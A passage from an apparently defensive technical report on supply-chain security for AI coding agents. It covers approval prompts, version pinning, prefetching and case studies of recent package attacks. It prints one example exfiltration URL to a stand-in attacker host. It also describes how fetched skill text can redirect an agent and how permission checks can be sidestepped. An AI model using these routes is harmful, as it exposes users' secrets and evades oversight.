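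The hook caught the fault in ten of the eleven scenarios tested. It missed a package recommended in an error message, because that package exists on PyPI and looks normal from outside. The models refused to install it in every run because the project's own files didn't mention it. The hook blocked the vulnerable versions that every model had installed, so the two checks complement each other.

The ten-of-eleven result tests whether the hook works as designed, because its makers wrote it with these scenarios in mind. Their estimate of false alarms is also narrow. The hook flagged five of the 1,000 most downloaded PyPI packages, but that sample includes no packages from other sources. By the study's description, the hook would also stop any project that has good reason to use another source, such as the one PyTorch, a machine-learning library, provides for some of its builds. Users would have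 to add such sources to the trusted list, and an agent trying to finish its task might propose doing that for them.

The hook checks the command but doesn't pin what the command will fetch. If someone approves `pip install examplelib`, the hook can confirm that the name is old and well known, but pip still chooses the version afterwards. A malicious new release of an established package would pass, because the age rule looks at the package's first release and the vulnerability list covers only problems already reported. The study acknowledges that a finished version should judge the resolved set of packages instead of the command, which would require the same information that a lockfile provides.

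Sharma and colleagues also point out that the hook misses some dependencies because it examines only install commands. Agents often write a dependency directly into a file, and a GitHub Actions workflow has no install command.

### Tools that start with the agent

In the cases so far, the agent proposed each download, and a person could at least have seen the command. Many agents also load code when a session begins, for example from a Model Context Protocol (MCP) server, which might give the agent access to a database or an issue tracker. The user lists the server and its start command in a configuration file, and the harness runs that command for each session.

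Anthropic's instructions for adding an MCP server use the example `npx -y airtable-mcp-server`, which specifies no version. In September 2026, *Scanning the Harness* found such declarations in 24.5% of the 1,063 setups with MCP servers, out of 2,660 working agent setups in public GitHub repositories. That share excludes 12 flagged setups, for reasons such as test files, templates and packages stored in the project itself.

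The scan covered what the files specify, not what happened when anyone ran them. Naming a package or image without a fixed version doesn't mean a new download at every start, because npx and Docker can reuse a copy on the machine, so the user can't easily predict when a new release will arrive. The repositories also came from curated lists, plugin marketplaces and projects that advertise their agent tooling, so the 24.5% may not hold for private company setups. On the other hand, the scan ignored transitive dependencies, and these can still change when the server's own version is fixed, as Corelight found.

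A person usually approves a server once. Anthropic lists a server that comes with a project as "Pending approval" until the user accepts it. According to a guide by HostTracker, a website-monitoring service, Claude Code asks the first time it sees such a server and remembers the answer for that project, while sessions that run without a user load the server without asking. The guide is unofficial and may be out of date, but if it is right, the approval covers the configuration entry, which doesn't change when a new release appears.

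*Scanning the Harness* recommends that harnesses show the resolved version of each server. This would also let a harness detect that the version had changed since the last session and ask for approval again.

### When the payload is text

A skill's payload can be plain-language instructions that the model reads and follows, so anyone who can change the text can change what the agent does without supplying any code. If the skill tells the agent to fetch its instructions from a web address, the text there can change after any review.

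For *Technical Report* (Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues, 2026), the security company Snyk scanned the skills on ClawHub, a public marketplace, and the 100 most used skills on another site, skills.sh. It also confirmed by hand that 76 skills were malicious. One category it looked for, "unverifiable dependencies", covers skills that fetch scripts, settings or instructions from outside when they run.

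| Group of skills | Share with unverifiable dependencies |
|---|---|
| All skills on ClawHub | 2.9% |
| Top 100 on skills.sh | 2.0% |
| Confirmed malicious skills | 21% |

The pattern is about seven times as common among the malicious skills, but 21% of 76 is only about 16 skills. The sample also leaves out malicious skills that the researchers' scanner misses, because they found the 76 by reviewing skills it had flagged. Most of the malicious skills didn't fetch content this way. An attacker who can publish a harmful skill openly has little need to hide the harmful part on a server, and eight of the 76 were still available when the study appeared.

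The study's main example, a skill published by Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, wasn't in the malicious group. The skill ran every few hours without supervision and, like many programs, updated itself. It told the agent to compare the skill's version number with the one on Moltbook's site and, if there was a newer version, to download the instruction files and save them over the old ones. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that this would let the site's operator, or presumably anyone who broke into the site, give new instructions to all its agents at once, which they put at 1.5 million users. They don't report that anyone did so.

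A command of this kind looks harmless at an approval prompt. It saves a text file and pipes nothing to a shell, so Monperrus's rule against piped downloads would allow it. The agent then reads the file, which doesn't look like running code either, and Claude Code doesn't ask for approval when an agent reads a file in the project.

Digests work on text as they do on programs, so a skill could name the digest of the instructions it fetches. Reviewing the text is harder, because its effect depends on the model that reads it and on what else that model has been told. Malware scanners look for harmful code, and instructions in ordinary English may contain none. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues advise skill authors to put everything a skill needs inside it and leave updates to the marketplace. A reviewer could then at least see the text the agent will read, although a marketplace update can change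 it too.

Fetched text is safer than fetched code in one way. An installed program can act at once, but a model that has read a harmful instruction still has to propose a command, which the harness can ask the user to approve. How much this helps depends on which commands the user has already allowed.

### What the prompt shows

*Setup Complete* ran Copilot CLI, Codex CLI and Cursor with options that execute commands without asking, and found no harness that checked packages automatically. Harnesses handle approvals differently, so the details below, which come from Claude Code's current documentation, may not apply to the others.

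Anthropic illustrates a prompt for the command `npm test`. It shows:

- a short description, "Run the test suite";
- the command itself;
- a line saying that the command requires approval;
- the choices to approve once, to approve and not be asked again for `npm test *`, to approve and switch to a mode in which a classifier reviews actions instead of the user, or to refuse.

That example doesn't show the user which code the command will run. `npm test` runs whatever test command the project's `package.json` contains, and the tests load the installed packages. For an install command, the same layout would show the package's name and any version given in the command, but not the release npm will choose or its dependencies. The pictured prompt also describes the command's purpose, but the user has no separate evidence that the description is accurate.

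### How a standing approval reaches later code

If the user chooses not to be asked again about a shell command, Claude Code saves a rule in a settings file at the root of the repository. The rule applies to every later session there until someone removes it, whereas permission to edit files ends with the session. For commands that fetch code, the command permission should be the shorter one, because a person can see an edit in full but not what a later install will fetch.

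The asterisk in a rule stands for any text, including spaces. Anthropic's documentation explains how far some rules reach, and the effect on fetched code follows from that:

| Rule | What it allows without asking | What can change later |
|---|---|---|
| `Bash(npm test *)` | The project's tests, with any options | The test files, the test command and every installed package |
| `Bash(npm install *)` | Installing any package | Everything, including the choice of package |
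| `Bash(npx *)` | Running any package | Everything, including the choice of package |
| `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` | Reading any page on that domain | Every page, including instructions that the model may follow |
| `mcp__puppeteer__*` | Every tool of the MCP server called `puppeteer` | The server's code and its list of tools |
| `Bash(docker run example/app@sha256:…)` | That exact command | Only what the image's program downloads for itself |

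The last rule has no asterisk and contains a digest, so a standing approval of it will cover the same image a year from now. The other rules cover whatever their names point to later. Anthropic warns about runners such as npx and advises writing a rule that includes both the runner and the inner command. This limits the approval to one package, but the rule still needs an exact version, and even then the package's dependencies can change.

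The permission rule for an MCP server contains the server's name but not its version. If npx starts a newer release tomorrow, the rule also applies to that release, including any tools it adds.

Claude Code limits some of these rules. It treats `|` and `&&` as separators and requires permission for each part, so a rule that allows `curl` doesn't cover `curl … | sh` unless another rule allows the shell. It also checks where a command writes its output, and asks the user about paths beginning with `~`, the user's home folder, even when a rule allows `curl`. The command in Moltbook's skill saves to such a path, so the user would see the address and the file name, but not the new instructions.

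Splitting commands can defeat the digest check described earlier, `echo "DIGEST  install.sh" | sha256sum -c - && sh install.sh`. When a user gives a standing approval to a joined command, Claude Code saves a separate rule for each part that needs one, and a rule for `sh install.sh` would allow the script to run without the check. A standing approval of the whole line protects the user only if the harness matches the line as a unit. To get the same protection in Claude Code, someone could write a small program that takes the digest and the file name, checks the file against the digest and runs it only if they match, so that the harness has a single command to match.

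A user may also inherit standing approvals, because Claude Code lets a team store its permission rules in the repository. *Scanning the Harness* found settings that allow any shell command, or broad use of a program that can run other code, in 67 of 2,660 setups. One example was `Bash(python:*)`, which allows any Python program. In another 101 setups, which may overlap with the 67, a skill's own file contained a similarly broad permission, which in Claude Code lasts until the user's next message. A skill that replaces its own file with a downloaded one could therefore gain new permissions as well as new instructions. The scan couldn't determine how many of these rules take effect, because that depends on the user's other settings and on whether the user has chosen to trust the project.

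Hooks are the main way to restore a check. Anthropic states that a hook can block a command even when a rule allows it, so a team could let `npm install` run without prompting the user and still have a program examine each install. The program could compare the resolved versions with the last approved set and prompt the user only when something had changed, which a rule based on the command's text can't do.

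## What does fetching everything before approval add?

A hook that compares resolved versions gives the person a better list to judge, but the code on that list still arrives after the approval. Prefetching reverses the order. The harness downloads everything the command needs, asks the person, and then runs the command from the stored copy. The download-once procedure for install scripts does this with a single file. For a project with dependencies, the harness would:

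1. resolve every reference to an exact version and digest;
2. download the files without running any code from them;
3. record the digest of each file;
4. show the person what it fetched;
5. after approval, install and run from the stored copy with the network off.

### What each step contributes

Resolution produces what a good lockfile already contains. Downloading the archives as well lets a colleague or a scanner open the files while the person is deciding, and the run won't fail later because a publisher has withdrawn a release.

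The recorded digests are used to check that the files that run are the ones somebody examined. They have to come from the user's side. PyPI adds a digest to every download address and pip checks it, but according to pip's *Secure installs*, this only protects against corrupted downloads, because the digest also comes from the remote server.

Switching off the network stops later downloads that a digest doesn't cover, such as a plugin that a program fetches when it starts. Unlike a lockfile, the offline run also tests whether the list is complete, because the run fails if the harness missed something the command needs.

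The operating system or a container has to block network access, because options such as pip's `--no-index` and npm's `--offline` govern only the package manager, and an install script can still call `curl`. The harness also has to keep the machine offline after the installation, or the program can download anything the next time it starts.

### A Python project from start to finish

Suppose an agent wants to run the tests of a small project whose `requirements.in` file contains one line, `examplelib==2.4.1`. The package names, dates and digests here are invented, but the commands are real. The harness starts a container that has a network connection and no passwords, and runs:

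```
pip-compile --generate-hashes --pip-args "--only-binary=:all:" \
  --output-file=requirements.txt requirements.in

python -m pip download --require-hashes --no-deps --only-binary :all: \
  -r requirements.txt --dest wheelhouse

sha256sum requirements.txt wheelhouse/*
```

`pip-compile` resolves the dependencies and writes each one to `requirements.txt` with an exact version and its digests. MLflow's *Secure Installs*, a guide for users of the machine-learning tool, recommends the same command. `pip-compile` is part of the pip-tools package, so the harness should keep a fixed copy of pip-tools as well.

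According to pip's documentation, `pip download` resolves and downloads packages as `pip install` does, but saves them in a folder instead of installing them. `--no-deps` stops it from adding anything that `requirements.txt` doesn't list, and `--only-binary :all:` restricts it to wheels. *Use “pip install” safely* recommends these two options and `--require-hashes` for ordinary installs too.

A version can have several correct digests, because publishers upload separate wheels for different systems and `requirements.txt` may list all their digests. The folder holds only the file that pip chose for this machine, so the harness should build the person's list from the folder. It can open the wheels, which are ZIP archives, and look up their upload dates on the registry. PyPI's *pip 26.3*, the page for a release of pip, gives an upload date and a SHA-256 digest for each file.

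On 12 May, the prompt might show this:

| Package | Version | Needed by | Published | SHA-256 | Code that runs at installation or when Python starts |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `examplelib` | 2.4.1 | The project | 3 February | `9f2c61d0…` | None |
| `exampleparse` | 1.9.0 | `examplelib` | 14 November | `41be07aa…` | None |
| `examplehttp` | 3.0.2 | `examplelib` | 11 May | `c85d3e19…` | None |
| `exampletrace` | 0.6.3 | `examplehttp` | 20 January | `07fa92b4…` | `exampletrace.pth`, whenever Python starts |

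Below the table, the prompt would show the digest of `requirements.txt` and the command waiting to run. The whole prompt would be short enough for a person to read, whereas pip's own locking command wrote a 519-line file when Willison (2026) ran it on two packages, Datasette and LLM.

Wheels don't have install scripts, but they can contain a `.pth` file, and Python runs any line in it that begins with `import` each time it starts. Someone reading this list would want to know why `exampletrace` needs one. They might also hesitate over `examplehttp`, which came out the day before and wasn't requested by name. pip's `--uploaded-prior-to P3D` option ignores files less than three days old if the registry supplies upload dates. Willison asked for a version of LLM at least four days old and got 0.30, because 0.31 was three days old.

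If the person approves, the harness checks the digest of `requirements.txt` again and runs:

```
docker run --rm --network none -v "$PWD":/work:ro -w /work \
  python:3.12.7-slim-bookworm@sha256:… sh -c '
    pip install --no-index --find-links wheelhouse --require-hashes \
      --no-deps --only-binary :all: -r requirements.txt &&
    python -m unittest'
```

`--network none` gives the container no network connection, and `:ro` prevents programs inside it from changing the project or the stored wheels. pip takes its files from the `wheelhouse` folder and checks each against the digests in `requirements.txt`. The earlier download should use the same image, so that pip picks wheels for the right system. According to pip's manual, the file produced by pip's locking command is likewise guaranteed only for the current Python version and platform.

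If another program replaces a wheel after the approval, pip stops. If `exampletrace` tries to send data when Python starts, the attempt fails because it has no network connection. If `examplelib` tries to download a data file on first use, the test that needs the file probably fails, and the developer can add the file to the stored set with its own digest.

A JavaScript project with a lockfile can follow the same order:

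```
npm ci --ignore-scripts --cache ./npm-store
npm ci --offline --cache ./npm-store
```

The first line downloads the archives and runs no install scripts. After approval, the harness runs the second line with the network off, and npm runs whichever install scripts the project allows. A script that tries to download a prebuilt program will fail, which is inconvenient, but the developer learns from it that the lockfile didn't cover everything.

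### Build tools that already work this way

Nix, a package manager that builds software from precise descriptions, makes this separation a rule. Ordinary builds have no network access, but a build step that has to download something can have it if its description states the digest of the result in advance. A participant in *Using fixed output paths for a derivation*, a discussion on the Nix forum, calls this a compromise. Nix computes the digest when the step finishes and fails the build if the two digests differ. It may keep the unexpected file in its store, but doesn't use it as the step's output.

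Nix's *Content-addressing derivation outputs* gives the example of GNU Hello 2.1.1, a small demonstration program, downloaded over plain HTTP. If that server disappears, the maintainer can switch to an FTP address elsewhere without rebuilding anything, because the digest hasn't changed. Neither address is secure, but this hardly matters for integrity because the digest is fixed.

A well-known mistake with this arrangement is to change the address to a newer release but forget to change the digest. Nix identifies the file by its name and digest, so the developer may keep getting the old file. For an approval, this is safer than the habit of entering a dummy digest, letting the build fail and copying the digest from the error message. That habit records the digest of whatever file the server sent that day.

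Bazel, Google's build tool, can also separate the two stages, but leaves more of the work to the user. `bazel fetch` downloads a project's outside dependencies, and `bazel build --nofetch` then builds without fetching any more. The rule that downloads an archive accepts a SHA-256 digest but doesn't require one. The fetching stage can run programs, and build steps can normally use the network unless the user turns that off.

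Vendoring is a simpler method, in which a project copies the source code of its dependencies into its own repository, for example with `go mod vendor` or `cargo vendor`, and builds from the copies. An approval that covers the repository's files, as Hossen proposes, then covers the dependencies too, and the code remains available if the publisher deletes it. However, the repository becomes much larger, and one update can change thousands of lines. The copies also need protection from the agent. Cargo stores a checksum for each vendored file, and the build fails if a file doesn't match, but an agent that can edit the file can also edit the checksum. Go doesn't check vendored code against `go.sum` when it builds.

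### Cloud coding agents

Several companies run coding agents on their own servers, where the user usually isn't present to approve each command. Approval there consists mainly of a setup that someone writes in advance and the network rules that apply afterwards.

| | Codex cloud | Claude Code cloud sessions | Copilot cloud agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| How a team prepares the machine | Setup script, or automatic installation for common package managers | Setup script | Steps in a workflow file |
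| Network during setup | On | Same level as the rest of the session | Outside the agent's firewall |
| Default network while the agent works | Off | Listed domains, including package registries | Listed domains, including package registries |
| Reuse of the prepared machine | Up to 12 hours | About seven days | None; the steps run when Copilot starts work |

Codex cloud comes closest to the order described above. According to OpenAI's *Cloud environments*, the setup script runs with internet access, then Codex removes any secrets the script used, and the agent starts work offline. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* lists prompt injection, theft of code or secrets, and malware among the reasons for this default. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* distinguishes the sandbox mode, which limits what Codex can technically do, from the approval policy, which determines when it has to ask. The offline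 restriction is part of the sandbox mode, so it works even if nobody reads any prompts.

However, being offline doesn't pin the versions the setup script fetched earlier. OpenAI's example script contains `pip install pyright`, with no version, so each rebuild of the environment can install a different release. On business plans, everyone with access to an environment shares the stored result, including any bad release in it.

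A team can also write a maintenance script, which runs when Codex reuses a stored machine. Codex checks out the task's branch first, so if the script runs `npm install`, that command installs the packages listed in the branch's `package.json`, which an agent may have edited during an earlier task. OpenAI runs this script before applying the agent's network settings, so it presumably has internet access. The team should have the script install the versions in a reviewed lockfile.

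Claude Code's cloud sessions don't separate the stages. Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* describes one network level for each environment, which also applies to its setup script. If the user selects "None", the script can't install packages from a registry. Users can't run setup with a connection and then cut it off, because changing the allowed hosts makes Anthropic rebuild the environment under the new rules. A team could instead commit its wheels to the repository and install them from there at the start of each session. At "None", GitHub operations and any connectors the user enables still work because they use separate channels.

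The default level, "Trusted", allows only listed domains, but anyone can publish on some of them. The list includes GitHub's gists (short public files), its server for raw repository files, and every address under `amazonaws.com`, where Amazon's customers store their own data. The list therefore doesn't stop an agent from piping a stranger's gist into a shell.

Copilot's firewall also allows package registries by default. GitHub says the firewall covers only processes the agent starts through its shell tool, not MCP servers, and that sophisticated attacks may get around it.

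GitHub's sample setup for Copilot uses `npm ci`, so it follows the lockfile. GitHub's *About customizing Copilot cloud agent's development environment* also explains that if a setup step fails, Copilot skips the remaining steps and starts working with the machine as it is. If `npm ci` stops because the lockfile is out of date, the agent can try to install the missing packages itself, since it can still reach the registry. A team that wants to enforce the lockfile has to remove the public registries from the firewall's allowlist.

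### Source packages that run code during a download

Downloading a Python package before approval often isn't harmless if the package is available only as source code, because pip may run its build program. In February 2025, zahlman, in *Python packaging*, built a tiny source package whose build program only exited with a message. `pip download` ran the program and printed the message, even though the file was already on the machine and the command set pip to ignore dependencies. zahlman traced this to a check in which pip builds the package's metadata to confirm its name and version, although both appeared in the file's name.

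Large packages have the same problem. A participant in the Python forum thread *Pip download (just the source packages, no building, no metadata, etc.)* found that pip had to install Cython and NumPy to finish downloading pandas, even with `--no-deps`.

zahlman also retells the experience of Brendan Dolan-Gavitt, a security researcher who in 2022 asked pip for a trial installation of all 397,267 packages then on PyPI, using the option that is supposed to install nothing. Some of the packages ran their code anyway. One tried to use `sudo`, the command for administrator rights, and others left pictures in his home folder.

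That year, *Automatic Execution of Code Upon Package Download on Python Package Manager*, by the security company Checkmarx, estimated that about a third of PyPI's packages would run code when downloaded. The share may have fallen since, as more publishers provide wheels, but it is a poor guide to the risk of deliberate attacks, because an attacker can leave the wheel out.

Requiring wheels solves this, but the requirement has to apply to resolution as well as to the download, so the example also passes the option to `pip-compile`. If a package has no wheel, zahlman advises getting the source file from PyPI's website or API, without using pip. The harness can then show the file to a reviewer and build it offline after approval.

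That build needs tools that an ordinary requirements file doesn't list. They used to be easier to overlook because pip applied the project's version constraints to them. According to PyPA's *Announcement* (2026), from the group that maintains pip, version 26.2 stopped doing this, and constraining build tools now requires a separate `--build-constraint` option. An offline build at least exposes a missing tool, because pip can't download it.

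### Downloads that send data out

Fetching before approval can leak data, because the request itself sends information to the server. An agent following an attacker's instructions could propose a script whose URL contains a stolen password, such as `https://attacker.example/a.sh?key=…`. If the harness downloads the script to show it to the user, the attacker gets the password before the user has read anything. A harness should prefetch automatically only from registries it knows, and ask before contacting any other server.

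### Packages and services the agent needs midway

An agent often discovers during a task that it needs another package, for example when a test fails on a missing import. GitHub describes Copilot's process of finding a project's dependencies by trial and error as "slow and unreliable", and recommends installing them in advance. The setup step can install the packages a project already uses, but not a library that the agent decides to add during the task.

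Users of Codex cloud have run into the simpler half of this problem. In *Codex cloud agent unable to install pnpm dependencies*, a thread on OpenAI's forum, one user wanted the agent to run `npm test` and fix any failures. Another replied that the install command had to go in the setup script. Once it was there, at least one participant still had trouble with one package, `onnxruntime-node`, and found it hard to investigate without a terminal.

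Some tasks need a live service that a stored copy can't replace. In *Codex internet access not working*, a user's tests failed because they couldn't reach the servers of Alpaca, a trading service. A reply blamed the way Node.js uses Codex's proxy, and another user had connection errors even with internet access turned on, so working offline doesn't fully explain the failures. Still, tests that call Alpaca need a connection. Developers can replace some services with a local database or recorded responses. For the rest, they can open the network to the hosts that the tests need, and OpenAI also lets them restrict the type of request. The approval then doesn't cover anything the program fetches from those hosts.

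The harness also has to handle failed installs. Version 26.2 of pip added `--no-require-hashes`, which disables the digest checks that pip otherwise turns on when a requirements file contains digests. An agent might well propose it to get past a mismatch, and the short option is easy to miss in a long command.

### Asking less often

If people are prompted for every fetch and every run, they will soon approve without looking. Suppose an agent runs the tests forty times in a day and adds one package. Only the new package needs a decision. A prepared environment, an approved mirror and a permission tied to the lockfile are each meant to limit prompts to cases like the new package.

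A mirror is a company's own copy of a registry. pip can use one through `--index-url`, which accepts any server that follows the standard index format or a local folder laid out the same way.

| | Prepared environment | Approved mirror | Automatic permission while the lockfile is unchanged |
|---|---|---|---|
| When a person decides | Before the session | When a package or version enters the mirror | When the lockfile changes |
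| What is fixed during a session | Everything installed, if the network stays off | The set of packages the agent can choose from | Every package in the lockfile |
| What happens when the agent needs a new package | It has to wait until someone changes the setup | It gets the package at once if the mirror has it | The person sees the proposed change |
| Main weakness | Floating versions resolve again at each rebuild | A mirror that copies every new release approves nothing | Install scripts can still download other code unless the network is off |

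A prepared environment suits repeated work on a stable project, where the agent rarely needs anything new. It produces no prompts, so nobody looks at what each rebuild fetches. The setup should therefore install from a lockfile.

The mirror moves the decision to someone better placed to make it, such as a company's security team. The agent can add an approved library mid-task, and one review serves every project. But many mirrors fetch a package from the public registry the first time anyone asks for it, which speeds up installs but adds no review. The firewall also has to block the public registry, because an agent can put that registry's address in its own command, and with `--extra-index-url` pip searches both places. GitHub's settings let an administrator turn off the recommended list and allow only a company address, or a single folder on it, such as `https://packages.contoso.corp/project-1/`.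 In Claude Code's cloud sessions, the "Custom" level can do the same for a whole domain.

Maintaining a reviewed mirror is a lot of work, so the lockfile rule is probably better for a single developer. The harness stores the digests of approved lockfiles where the agent can't change them. When the agent proposes the offline install, the harness compares the current lockfile's digest with the stored ones. If it matches one, the command runs without a prompt. In the example day, the person would see one prompt, listing the new package and whatever came with it.

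The rule should apply only to the exact command that installs from the stored copy with the network off. The comparison also has to include `package.json` and `.npmrc`, because both affect which install scripts run.

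## Would a fixed payload have stopped recent attacks?

Lockfiles, digests and stored copies preserve the code that someone chose at a particular moment. How much this helps depends on whether the user chose it before or after the attacker changed it. The table applies this test to six attacks between 2024 and 2026. In the five most recent, the attackers were after passwords and access tokens on developers' machines and build servers.

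The last three columns are inferred from the reported facts, not measured. The accounts of these attacks don't include how many victims had a lockfile or a pinned digest, so the table can show only what these protections should have done.

| Attack | What changed | When | Payload fixed before the attack | Payload first fetched during the attack | What prefetching adds to a first fetch |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
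| xz Utils | Two official releases contained a backdoor | February–March 2024 | Safe | Malicious, and a pin preserves it | Little, because the backdoor was well hidden |
| `tj-actions/changed-files` | Existing tags moved to a malicious commit | 14–15 March 2025 | Safe with a commit hash, exposed with a tag | Malicious, and a hash copied from the tag preserves it | A chance to read the new code |
| Trivy | Existing action tags moved; new malicious releases and images appeared | 19–22 March 2026 | Safe with a commit hash or image digest, exposed with an action tag | Malicious, and a pin preserves it | A chance to read the new code |
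| TanStack | 84 new versions of 42 npm packages | 11 May 2026 | Safe with a lockfile | Malicious, and the lockfile preserves it | A strange dependency and a large extra file to notice |
| AntV | 639 new versions of 323 npm packages | 19 May 2026 | Safe with a lockfile | Malicious, and the lockfile preserves it | A new install script to notice |
| keyv worm | New versions of hundreds of npm packages | From 4 August 2026 | Safe with a lockfile | Malicious, and the lockfile preserves it | A new install script to notice |

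### Tags that moved

The `tj-actions/changed-files` action lists the files that a pull request or commit changes. More than 20,000 repositories used it, according to CNCF TAG Security's *tj-actions/changed-files GitHub Action Compromise*. The attacker disguised a malicious commit as the work of Renovate, a tool that automates dependency updates, and added it to a real Renovate pull request, which the project merged automatically. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reports that the attacker then moved the action's existing tags to the new commit. The affected tags ran from `v1` to `v45.0.7`, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-30066 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database.

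Even if a workflow's owner had read every line of release `v35` a year before the attack and referred to it by that tag ever since, the next run after the attack would still have used the attacker's code. Only pinning the workflow to a commit hash recorded beforehand would have prevented this.

An update tool can undo that protection, because such tools often replace an old hash with the one the newest tag points to. If a tool had done this on 14 March, it would have written the malicious hash into the workflow beside a familiar version number.

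The malicious code searched the build server's memory for secrets and printed them in the workflow's log, which anyone can read if the repository is public (Ecosyste.ms, a site that collects security advisories). But CNCF TAG Security says the code sent the secrets to an outside server. The first account fits better with CISA's advice, since the agency asks owners of public repositories to check for exposed keys and warns that the text may be encoded twice. If the secrets went to the log, switching off the network would not have protected them.

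CISA lists a compromise of another action, `reviewdog/action-setup@v1`, as a possible cause of the attack. That compromise lasted less than two hours on 11 March. A user's pin can't prevent a break-in like this at the publisher, but it does keep the resulting code out of the user's workflow.

A year later, Aqua Security's vulnerability scanner, Trivy, suffered a similar attack. According to BoostSecurity's *20 Days Later*, an attacker took over one of Aqua's service accounts on 19 March 2026, published a malicious version 0.69.4 of Trivy and moved 75 of the 76 tags on its GitHub Action. CrowdStrike's *From Scanner to Stealer* counts 76 of 77. The malicious code ran before the real scanner, so the workflows appeared to finish normally. NHS Digital (2026) advised anyone who had named a tag instead of a full commit hash to check their logs for 19 and 20 March.

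Three days later, two more malicious Trivy images appeared on Docker Hub, tagged `0.69.5` and `0.69.6`. Neither had a matching release or tag on GitHub, according to a message on an Openwall mailing list (Openwall, 2026). Because these tags were new, a command that named an older image was unaffected even without a digest. A harness that compared Docker Hub with GitHub could have caught the missing releases.

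A harness might also use a scanner like Trivy to examine fetched code before asking for approval. If the harness had fetched the newest version for each check, the check itself would have run the credential stealer, so the scanner needs to be pinned too.

### Six minutes at TanStack

TanStack is a family of JavaScript libraries for building web applications. One of them, `@tanstack/react-router`, has more than 12 million downloads a week. Attackers published malicious versions of 42 packages within six minutes without stealing any npm password (InfoQ, *TanStack Details Sophisticated npm Supply Chain Attack That Compromised 42 Packages*, 2026).

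The attackers opened a pull request from their own copy of the project. One of TanStack's workflows automatically built the proposed code to measure its size. That build left altered package files in a cache, where GitHub keeps downloaded files for later workflows to reuse. Eight hours later, the release workflow loaded the cache and ran the attackers' code. The code then read a publishing token from the machine's memory and sent the malicious packages directly to npm.

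These times come from TanStack's own account, which traeai's *Postmortem* reproduces:

| Time on 11 May (UTC) | Event | What a new installation could fetch |
|---|---|---|
| 11:29 | The altered files enter the cache | Clean version |
| 11:31 | The attacker empties the pull request and closes it | Clean version |
| 19:15 | A maintainer merges an unrelated fix, which starts the release workflow | Clean version |
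| 19:20 | The first malicious versions appear on npm | Malicious version |
| 19:26 | The second set appears | Malicious version |
| About 19:50 | An outside researcher reports the attack | Malicious version |
| About 21:00 | TanStack starts to mark the affected versions as deprecated | Malicious version, until npm removes it |

A project with a lockfile from before 19:20 would have kept its old versions, and `npm ci` would have installed them throughout the evening. A project without a lockfile could have received the malicious code even with a narrow version range such as `~1.169.0`, which allows both bad releases of `@tanstack/react-router`, 1.169.5 and 1.169.8.

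The danger lasted much longer than the six minutes it took to publish the packages. npm doesn't let publishers withdraw most packages that other packages depend on, so TanStack had to ask npm's staff to remove the files, which added hours. OSV's *GHSA-g7cv-rxg3-hmpx* (2026), TanStack's official advisory, recommends auditing build servers that installed the packages between 19:20 and 19:30, a window that seems too short given how long the files stayed available. Elsewhere, the advisory treats every installation of an affected version that day as compromised, which is the safer rule.

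TanStack had a lockfile too, and it didn't protect the release. The workflow named its cache after the lockfile's digest. Because the lockfile was public, the attackers could compute the name in advance and store their files under it. TanStack didn't explain in its account whether anything compared the restored files with the digests in the lockfile. A harness that prefetches packages has the same weakness if other programs can write to its store. It should prevent those writes and check each file again at installation.

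The attackers pinned their own payload. Each malicious package had an optional dependency on `github:tanstack/router#79ac49ee…`, pinned to a full commit hash. The address names the original repository, but the commit came from an outsider's fork, as can also happen with GitHub Actions.

npm 12, which came out two months later, refuses Git dependencies by default and would have blocked this route.

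### Bursts at AntV and keyv

Eight days after the TanStack attack, someone used a stolen maintainer account to publish malicious versions of AntV, a set of charting libraries, and of other packages the account controlled. The Hacker News, a security news site, cites a count of 639 versions of 323 packages. The security company SafeDep counted 637 versions of 317 packages, all published within 22 minutes. At about 29 versions a minute, nobody could have reviewed them as they appeared.

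The affected packages included `echarts-for-react`, which has about 1.1 million downloads a week and doesn't have "antv" in its name. A developer could therefore have installed a malicious version without knowing that the project used anything from AntV's maintainers. Some of the packages had been dormant, according to VPNCentral's *Over 600 npm package versions hit in Mini Shai-Hulud supply chain attack*. A floating version still allows a dormant package's next release to be installed, even if the package seems safe because it hasn't changed. A list of versions with their release dates would draw attention to a sudden new release of a dormant package.

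The August attack began with keyv, a small library for storing data. OpenNET, a Russian technology news site, reports that keyv has 154 million downloads a week and that 1,703 packages depend on it. On 4 August the attackers published a malicious version, 6.0.0. It contained a worm, a program that copies itself, which Elastic Security Labs calls ChainDrop. The worm looked for npm credentials on each machine where someone installed the package and used them to publish infected versions of the owner's other packages.

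Because `keyv` 6.0.0 was a new major version, a project that asked for `^5.0.0` would not have received it, but `npm install keyv` would have installed it. The related package `flat-cache` was more dangerous for existing projects because its malicious version, 6.1.24, was a patch release. Any project with the rule `^6.1.0` and no lockfile would have installed it. Datadog Security Labs traced nine such releases to the five minutes from 10:09 to 10:14 UTC.

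Estimates of the worm's reach vary widely:

| Source of the count | Malicious versions | Packages |
|---|---|---|
| SafeDep, verified in the registry | 353 | 79 |
| Aikido, a security company | 1,381 | at least 868 |
| OpenNET | 2,212 | 444 |

*Keyv-Linked npm Worm Poisons Hundreds of Packages* (The Hacker News, 2026) reports SafeDep's and Aikido's figures and notes that nobody could reproduce the larger total from a complete public list. *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs* (Muncaster, 2026) puts the number of packages at more than 400. The counts were made at different times with different methods, so they don't show which company was most accurate.

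Most of these packages relied on install scripts. npm 12, which blocks these scripts by default, had been out for weeks by then, so the worm presumably spread through older versions of npm and through projects that had allowed the scripts. An up-to-date npm would not have stopped every package in this series of attacks. A malicious Python package from May, `guardrails-ai` 0.10.1, ran its code when a program imported it, then downloaded a second program and ran that without checking its integrity (The Hacker News).

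### Before the attack or during it

The same rule explains all the npm rows in the table. Let a be the time when malicious code becomes available under a name, r the time when the registry removes it, and f the time when the user fixes the payload:

- if f < a, the user keeps the old code;
- if a ≤ f < r, the user keeps the attacker's code;
- if f ≥ r, the user gets clean code again.

A floating version has no single f, because each new resolution can choose different code. Suppose a malicious release stays available for three hours. A build server that resolves its dependencies from scratch every hour will install it about three times. If the same project used a lockfile and refreshed it once a week at a random hour, the chance of refreshing within those three hours would be 3 in 168, or 1.8%. The lockfile reduces exposure by making refreshes less frequent, though each refresh is no safer.

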